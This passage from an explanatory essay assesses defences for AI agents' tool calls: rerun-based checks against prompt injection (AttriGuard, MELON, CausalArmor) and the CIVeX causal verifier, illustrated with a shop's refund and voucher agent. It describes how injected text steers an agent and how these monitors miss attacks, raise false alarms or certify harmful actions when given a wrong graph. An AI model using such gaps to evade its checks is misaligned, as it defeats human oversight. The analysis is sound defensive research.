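AttriGuard should be less vulnerable to this objection, because its rewriting is meant to preserve facts such as account numbers. Ahad and colleagues ran it 240 times on authorised calls from the 24 cases and 240 times on unauthorised ones. It blocked 47% of the authorised calls and 36% of the unauthorised ones. This difference could be due to chance, since the 95% confidence interval runs from blocking authorised calls 36 percentage points more often to blocking them 15 points less often. The test gives no evidence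 that AttriGuard blocks unauthorised calls more often than authorised ones.

The judging step rejected 85% of the unauthorised calls it received and 66% of the authorised ones. But a call reaches the judge only if the rerun proposes different arguments. The rerun reproduced the unauthorised call exactly in 138 of 240 runs, and AttriGuard let it through. It reproduced the authorised call in only 70, and Ahad and colleagues couldn't establish why the counts differed.

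He and colleagues anticipated part of the objection. They accept that the more a user lets outside data determine an action, the less the data need to steer the agent. In their view, the attribution is still correct in such cases, but it can't show whether the data are authentic. That defends the definition, but a shop that relies on AttriGuard to protect payments would still lose money. He and colleagues recommend asking the user to confirm a suspicious call instead of blocking it. Ahad and colleagues recommend checking authority separately. For the shop, this could be a permission that allows refunds only to the account on file for the customer the employee named.

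### False alarms and misses

A strict counterfactual would keep the model's random choices the same and change only the data. A rerun makes new random choices, so a legitimate refund may disappear by chance. Tests by He and colleagues used the least random settings and still produced slightly different results between runs, which they attribute mainly to providers sending requests to different machines or software versions.

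More reruns can reduce this kind of error. Suppose a legitimate refund reappears in 90% of reruns and a fraudulent one in 5%. With one rerun, the shop wrongly flags 10% of legitimate refunds and misses 5% of fraudulent ones. If it reruns the agent five times and follows the majority, those rates fall to about 0.9% and 0.1%, but the reruns take five times as much compute.

This test works only if rewriting the data leaves the task intact. If the helper model drops Ann's order number, her refund may reappear in only 40% of reruns. A single rerun then gives a false alarm 60% of the time, and a majority vote over five reruns does so 68% of the time. More reruns measure the effect of the rewriting more precisely, but they can't separate the effect of removing the steering from the effect of changing the facts.

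Zhu and colleagues give a formula for many reruns with different neutral requests. If the average similarity between the original call and the reruns is μ for a harmless call, and the alarm threshold θ is higher, the probability of a false alarm after n independent reruns is at most

exp(−2n(θ − μ)²)

For μ = 0.3, θ = 0.5 and n = 100, the bound is about 0.03%. The paper gives 0.018% for this example, which doesn't match its formula. The bound requires harmless calls to fall below the threshold on average, and some don't. MELON raised a false alarm on 9 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks, and in all nine the user had told the agent to carry out instructions from an outside source, such as a to-do list on a website. Zhu and colleagues regard these as real security risks, but a user who wrote the list herself would disagree.

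Measuring how often such tests are right requires agent runs in which the true cause of an action is known. *Long-Horizon Agent Trajectory Attribution* (Chen, Sun and colleagues, 2026) provides more than 1,300 runs, each labelled with the main cause of a chosen action. Language models helped write the labels, and people checked them.

At the shop, a false alarm means Ann gets her $40 late or not at all. The harm depends on what happens next. MELON abandons the whole task. CausalArmor only cleans some text and asks the agent again, which takes time and may remove something useful. If AttriGuard blocks a call, the agent can look for another way but may not find one.

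Ahad and colleagues followed AttriGuard to the end of 420 runs on 14 tasks. Some runs had no added text, while others had added text that agreed or conflicted with the user's request. The table shows how many runs out of 70 ended in each outcome.

| Added text | Unauthorised outcome: without / with AttriGuard | Authorised outcome: without / with AttriGuard |
|---|---|---|
| None | 0 / 0 | 41 / 35 |
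| Agrees with the user | 0 / 0 | 60 / 52 |
| Conflicts with the user | 17 / 2 | 38 / 47 |

AttriGuard prevented most of the unauthorised outcomes. The changes in authorised outcomes may be due to chance, because there were only 14 tasks. When the text conflicted with the request, AttriGuard blocked 13 unauthorised calls, and in 12 of these runs the agent went on to do what the user wanted. It also blocked nine calls that the user had authorised, and none of those runs achieved the authorised outcome. In the version tested, blocking one call could leave a later one unchecked. The researchers restored the check with a small code change and reported the fault.

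False alarms can outnumber real ones even when the test is fairly accurate. If 10 of 10,000 complaints contain an attack and the test wrongly flags 2% of the rest, employees will see about 200 false alarms and at most 10 real ones.

If the causal test misses an attacker's call, the agent carries it out, and the shop may not get the money back. The miss can also go unnoticed, because Ann may receive her refund in the same run. The $200 limit still applies to any call that passes the test.

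## Estimating the effect of an action before taking it

A tool call can follow every rule, come from a genuine request, and still make things worse. Suppose the shop's agent gives vouchers to some customers who complain, to encourage them to stay. The shop has records of who received a voucher, who was already a loyal customer, and who was still buying a year later.

| | Stayed, with a voucher | Stayed, without a voucher |
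|---|---|---|
| Loyal customers | 80% | 85% |
| New customers | 30% | 35% |
| All customers in the records | 70% | 45% |

In each group, customers with a voucher were 5 percentage points less likely to stay. In the records as a whole, they were 25 points more likely to stay. This happens because the agent gave most of its vouchers to loyal customers. Recipients were 80% loyal and the others 20% loyal, so the overall rates are

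0.8 × 80% + 0.2 × 30% = 70% with a voucher, and

0.2 × 85% + 0.8 × 35% = 45% without.

To remove the effect of loyalty, the shop can apply the same mix of customers to both columns. This is called *adjustment*. If half of all customers are loyal, the rates become

0.5 × 80% + 0.5 × 30% = 55% if everyone gets a voucher, and

0.5 × 85% + 0.5 × 35% = 60% if nobody does.

So vouchers lower retention by 5 points, provided that loyalty is the only common cause of getting a voucher and staying.

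### When the records can't give an answer

Now suppose the shop never recorded loyalty, and half of its customers got vouchers. It knows only the 70% and the 45%. If everyone had received a voucher, the actual recipients who stayed would make up 35% of all customers. The other half never had a voucher, so anywhere from none to all of them might have stayed with one. Retention with vouchers for everyone is therefore between 35% and 85%. By the same reasoning, retention without any vouchers is between 22.5% and 72.5%. The effect lies between

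35 − 72.5 = −37.5 points and 85 − 22.5 = +62.5 points.

Data from more customers wouldn't narrow this range. For a yes-or-no outcome, it is always 100 percentage points wide and includes zero, because the shop sees what each customer does either with a voucher or without one, but never both. Without further assumptions, the shop can't tell whether vouchers help.

An effect is *identifiable* if the causal graph and the distribution of the recorded variables are enough to compute it. *CausalDS* (Leban, Saarinen and Sun, 2026) uses this definition in a test for data-analysis agents, and the correct response to some of its tasks is to decline to answer. The effect of vouchers is identifiable if the shop recorded loyalty and there is no other common cause. If the shop didn't record loyalty, a verifier should refuse to estimate the effect.

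An ordinary confidence interval doesn't protect against this mistake. With 10,000 customers in the proportions above, the raw difference of 25 points has a lower 95% confidence limit of about 23 points. More data would narrow the interval around the same wrong number.

### How CIVeX decides

*CIVeX* (Rovai, 2026) proposes a verifier that treats each state-changing tool call as an intervention. The call may run only with a *causal certificate*, which records why the action should help and which assumptions that depends on. The shop would have to supply its records, a measure of success (here retention) and a causal graph. The graph is *committed*, meaning that somebody fixes it in advance and CIVeX neither learns nor tests it. A two-headed arrow between the action and the outcome marks an unrecorded common cause.

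CIVeX then handles a call as follows:

1. Calls that only look something up or calculate something run immediately. CIVeX rejects malformed calls and forbidden types of action.
2. For any other call, it searches the graph for a way to compute the effect. Usually this means finding recorded variables to adjust for, such as loyalty. It can also use a recorded intermediate step through which the action has its whole effect, if the hidden cause doesn't influence that step directly.
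3. If the effect is identifiable, CIVeX estimates it and calculates a one-sided lower confidence limit, which exceeds the true effect at most 5% of the time. If this limit is at least zero and the action's cost is acceptable, the verdict is *execute*. Otherwise it is *reject*.
4. If the effect isn't identifiable, the verdict is *experiment* when the action is cheap enough and reversible, and *abstain* when it isn't.

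In Rovai's example, an agent wants to add an index to a database table to speed up queries. According to the graph, query and write volumes affect both the decision and the time saved. After adjusting for them, CIVeX estimates a saving of 3.10 milliseconds with a lower limit of 2.85, so the agent may proceed. The certificate contains the graph, the assumptions, the identification argument, the estimate and its lower limit, a fingerprint of the data and an upper limit on potential harm. The harm limit is 0.05, the same as the action's stated cost, so CIVeX seems to take it as given instead of estimating it.

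With loyalty recorded for 10,000 customers, the vouchers' estimated effect is −5 points and the lower limit is about −6.7, so CIVeX would reject them. If loyalty were missing but the graph had a two-headed arrow, CIVeX would call for an experiment or abstain. All these estimates are averages, so an action that drives some customers away can still get a certificate if it keeps enough others.

### The two propositions

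Rovai proves lower bounds on the harm caused by a verifier that approves an action whenever the records show a positive association. A trap is an action that is harmful but looks helpful in the records. If a fraction p of proposals are traps, the verifier executes harmful actions at a rate of at least p. Over H proposals, its expected loss is at least p × H × the average harm of a trap. These bounds follow almost immediately from the definition of a trap, so their practical importance depends on how common traps are.

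The other proposition limits CIVeX's own errors. If the confidence limit has a 5% error rate, the probability that CIVeX executes an action with a negative effect is at most 5%. The proof is short. CIVeX executes only if the lower limit is at least zero, so a harmful action can pass only if the limit is above the true effect, which happens at most 5% of the time. The proposition needs four assumptions:

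- One customer's treatment doesn't affect another customer. This fails if customers tell each other how to get vouchers.
- The committed graph is correct.
- Every type of customer had some chance of getting a voucher and some chance of not getting one.
- The estimate and its confidence limit are statistically valid.

The 5% bound applies to all proposals, including the ones CIVeX refuses. Suppose the agent proposes 1,000 actions, of which 980 are harmful. CIVeX could execute 49 of the harmful ones and all 20 helpful ones without breaking the bound, and 71% of the executed actions would then be harmful. Rovai states in the text that the bound is not a rate among executed actions, but describes it as one in the abstract.

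### Causal-ToolBench

Rovai tested CIVeX on Causal-ToolBench, a set of 1,890 generated decisions in six families of workflow: adding database indexes, restarting services, migrating data, caching, keeping logs and managing code branches. Only the names come from real work, since each case is a small structural causal model that generates a table of numbers, with no database or agent. Roughly half of the actions in each family are harmful, so a verifier can't tell from the family's name whether an action is safe.

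In the moderate cases, hidden confounding is weak or absent. In the adversarial cases, a strong hidden cause makes harmful actions look helpful and helpful ones look harmful. The utility score adds the size of an action's effect for executing a helpful action or refusing a harmful one. It subtracts the full size of the effect for executing a harmful action, and 30% of it for refusing a helpful one. "False executions" are harmful actions that the verifier allowed, as a share of all proposals.

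| Verifier | Moderate: false executions | Moderate: utility | Adversarial: false executions | Adversarial: utility |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Knows the true effect | 0% | 2.90 | 0% | 2.76 |
| CIVeX | 0% | 2.29 | 0% | 2.23 |
| Claude Opus 4.7, reasoning step by step | 0.2% | 2.28 | 0% | 1.65 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6, reasoning step by step | 2.3% | 2.08 | 1.0% | 1.82 |
| Refuses everything | 0% | 1.43 | 0% | 0.99 |
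| Goes by the recorded association | 0% | 2.90 | 28.3% | −0.27 |
| Checks only the form of the call | 50.3% | −0.64 | 45.5% | −0.03 |

The Claude models received the same graph and a summary of the data. Opus made almost no false executions, but in the adversarial cases it often abstained where CIVeX ran an experiment. In the moderate cases, relying on the recorded association gave a perfect score, so CIVeX's caution lowered utility by 0.61 points and prevented no harm. CIVeX is worth that loss only where strong confounding is a real possibility.

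The adversarial result depends entirely on the simulated experiments. When Rovai replaced every experiment with an abstention, CIVeX scored 0.99, the same as refusing everything. The graph already marks the hidden cause, so CIVeX never relies on the misleading records. It requests an experiment instead, and the benchmark supplies a second table in which treatment was assigned at random. These experiments are unusually informative. Under the settings in Rovai's follow-up paper, a typical effect is between 2 and 3.5 and the standard error of an experiment with 500 rows is about 0.24, so an experiment is very unlikely to get the sign wrong.

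If the 1,890 cases are independent, the absence of false executions supports an upper bound of 0.16% on the rate of false executions, by the formula for clean test records. But the cases come in seven batches, and for generalising, Rovai recommends a much weaker upper bound of 43% on the share of batches with a false execution.

Two further tests used data from outside the benchmark. One combined the characteristics of infants in a real medical trial with simulated outcomes. CIVeX made 10 false executions in 7,470 decisions, or 0.13%, compared with 6.5% for treating every infant. The other used real logs from ZOZO, an online fashion retailer, to identify items with above-average click rates. CIVeX made no false executions, whereas half of the items picked by a naive method were wrong. Both methods got only 56% of items right overall. Rovai concludes that the zero false-execution rate carries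 over to real production logs, but only 48 items had enough data, and choosing an item to display is very different from letting an agent delete a database.

### One wrong arrow

The committed graph is part of the trusted base, and Rovai states that the safety guarantee holds only if the graph is correct. One test in the original paper replaced recorded confounders in the graph with a two-headed arrow, which left the graph with less information but no false claims. CIVeX still made no false executions, though in the worst case it executed only 17.9% of actions correctly, down from 32.4%.

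The only published tests of CIVeX appear to be by its designer. In the most severe one, *Who Verifies the Graph?*, Rovai (2026) changed only the graph, keeping the same data and software. In the adversarial cases, removing the two-headed arrow raised false executions from zero to 15.3% of all actions, and 91% of the actions that CIVeX executed were harmful, though every one had a valid certificate. The shop would make this mistake if it had no record of loyalty and drew a graph without a hidden common cause. CIVeX would then certify the vouchers based on the 25 points.

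Reversing an arrow in the graph did even more damage. Suppose vouchers please customers but also teach them to wait for discounts, and customers who wait eventually leave. If the graph shows waiting as a cause of vouchers instead of a result, CIVeX compares only customers who wait to the same degree. Its estimate then includes the benefit of pleasing customers but omits the harm of teaching them to wait. In Rovai's version of this error, 48.9% of all actions were false executions and none were correct executions.

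Leaving out the two-headed arrow can also be harmless. When the hidden cause was weak, the graph without the arrow scored 2.79, against 2.27 for the correct graph, because CIVeX skipped unnecessary experiments. The certificate looks the same whether or not the omission does harm, because the graph doesn't include the hidden cause.

Rovai's remedy is to run an experiment before executing a certified action. If the experiment's confidence interval doesn't overlap with the certificate's, the check discards the certificate and bases its decision on the experiment. The table gives results for 1,050 actions in the adversarial setting.

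| Graph and check | Experiments | False executions | Helpful actions never executed | Utility |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Correct graph | 741 | 0% | 28.1% | 2.27 |
| Hidden cause omitted, no check | 0 | 15.3% | 97.1% | 0.35 |
| Hidden cause omitted, executions checked | 127 | 0% | 98.0% | 1.10 |
| Hidden cause omitted, rejections checked as well | 741 | 0% | 28.1% | 2.27 |

Checking executions stopped the harm but left almost all the helpful actions undone, because the wrong graph also led the agent to reject actions confidently. Those errors are hard to notice because a voucher that was never sent leaves no result to compare with the prediction, whereas a bad voucher eventually leads to a lost customer. Recovering the lost actions took another 614 experiments, which brought the total to the same number the correct graph had required.

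The zero false executions in the third row also depend on refusing the roughly 30% of actions for which no experiment was available. When Rovai allowed those actions, the false execution rate was 4.3%.

### Who could supply the graph

Rovai suggests asking experts for a candidate graph, using earlier trials where they exist, and checking the graph against held-out experimental data. A signed registry would then store each version. Rovai leaves this infrastructure to others.

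Experts don't always agree on a causal graph. *Realizing LLMs' Causal Potential Requires Science-Grounded, Novel Benchmarks* (Srivastava, Nagalapatti and colleagues, 2025) describes a graph for Alzheimer's disease that five specialists helped to draw. Their individual graphs differed substantially, and the final version kept an arrow if at least two of the five agreed on it. A shop's managers are unlikely to agree more closely about why customers leave.

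Language models could draft graphs with far less effort, but the evidence so far is discouraging. Srivastava and colleagues measured accuracy with F1, a score from 0 to 1 that is high only if most of the proposed arrows are right and few true ones are missing. A method based on a language model scored 0.93 on a well-known older graph and 0.54 on the new Alzheimer's graph. The researchers argue that models have memorised the older graph, since GPT-4 could fill in missing parts of such graphs almost perfectly. Combining the model's answer with a statistical analysis of data raised the score on the new graph to 0.67.

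In *From Causal Plausibility to Causal Reliability*, Kumar, Adl Zarabi and colleagues (2026) asked 12 open models about every ordered pair of variables in six published graphs. The models proposed far too many arrows. On a medical graph called Hepar2, the larger models found 59% of the true arrows on average, but only 9% of the arrows they proposed were correct. When the true arrow ran the other way, the models accepted the reversed one 36% of the time, usually with a stated confidence of at least 80%. The published graphs may leave out some real links, so some of the arrows counted as wrong may be correct.

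Some of these errors matter more than others for CIVeX. An unnecessary arrow from a customer's past orders may only add a harmless adjustment, while a reversed arrow can lead CIVeX to certify a harmful action. Kumar and colleagues also asked only about variables on a given list, but the shop's main danger is a common cause that nobody thought to list.

The newest models are much better at reasoning from a description that already contains the causal structure. In CausalDS, each task comes with a table of data and a short story describing what affects what, including any unrecorded causes. GPT-6 Astra passed 96% of the tasks with right-or-wrong answers, and Claude Opus 4.8 passed 81%. These tasks include recognising that an effect isn't identifiable. Each run had only about 34 such tasks, but the result suggests that a current model might do better than Opus 4.7 did in Rovai's comparison.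 This result doesn't help the shop find the causal structure, because Leban and colleagues used software to check that each story matched its graph.

### Drift and experiments on customers

A correct graph can also go out of date. Rovai proposes monitoring the variables used for adjustment and checking the graph again when their distribution changes. At the shop, this would detect a rise in the share of new customers, but not a competitor starting to match every voucher, because that changes how customers respond without changing who they are.

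The shop could detect such a change by continuing to choose at random whether some customers get a voucher. For an 80% chance of detecting a drop in retention from 60% to 55% at the usual 5% significance level, it needs about 1,500 customers with a voucher and 1,500 without. If vouchers do lower retention by 5 points, the shop will lose about 75 customers because of the trial. Causal-ToolBench understates the burden of such a trial, since it deducts only 0.05 points of utility for an experiment, about 2% of a typical effect.

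Agents may also be poor experimenters. *CausaLab* (Yang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) gave agents a simulated laboratory in which hidden equations determine the properties of crystals. In a version with six variables, GPT-5.2 predicted the right value in 92% of cases from past measurements alone, but its causal graphs had an F1 of 0.47. When it could also run experiments, the F1 rose to 0.80 but the share of correct predictions fell to 80%. Agents often settled on an answer too early. Both successful and failed runs left about half of the permitted experiments unused, and in failed runs the final explanation contradicted the agent's own data. Asking the agent to check its explanation against the data raised accuracy from 48% to 60% in a simpler version of the task. A shop would therefore do better to fix the size and analysis of a trial in advance than to let the agent decide when to stop.

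Whether a trial is acceptable also depends on what it withholds. Nobody is owed a voucher, so giving them out at random wrongs no one, at least if the shop caps the number. Refusing refunds at random would cheat people whose kettles were broken. CIVeX's test for an experiment covers only cost and reversibility, so the shop would need a separate permission requirement to rule out the refund trial.

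Some actions can't be tried first because the shop can't undo them. For example, the agent might propose deleting the accounts of customers who complain often. CIVeX would abstain if the graph contained a hidden common cause. If the graph contained none, CIVeX could certify the deletions from past records, and the shop couldn't safely run an experiment to check whether the graph was wrong.
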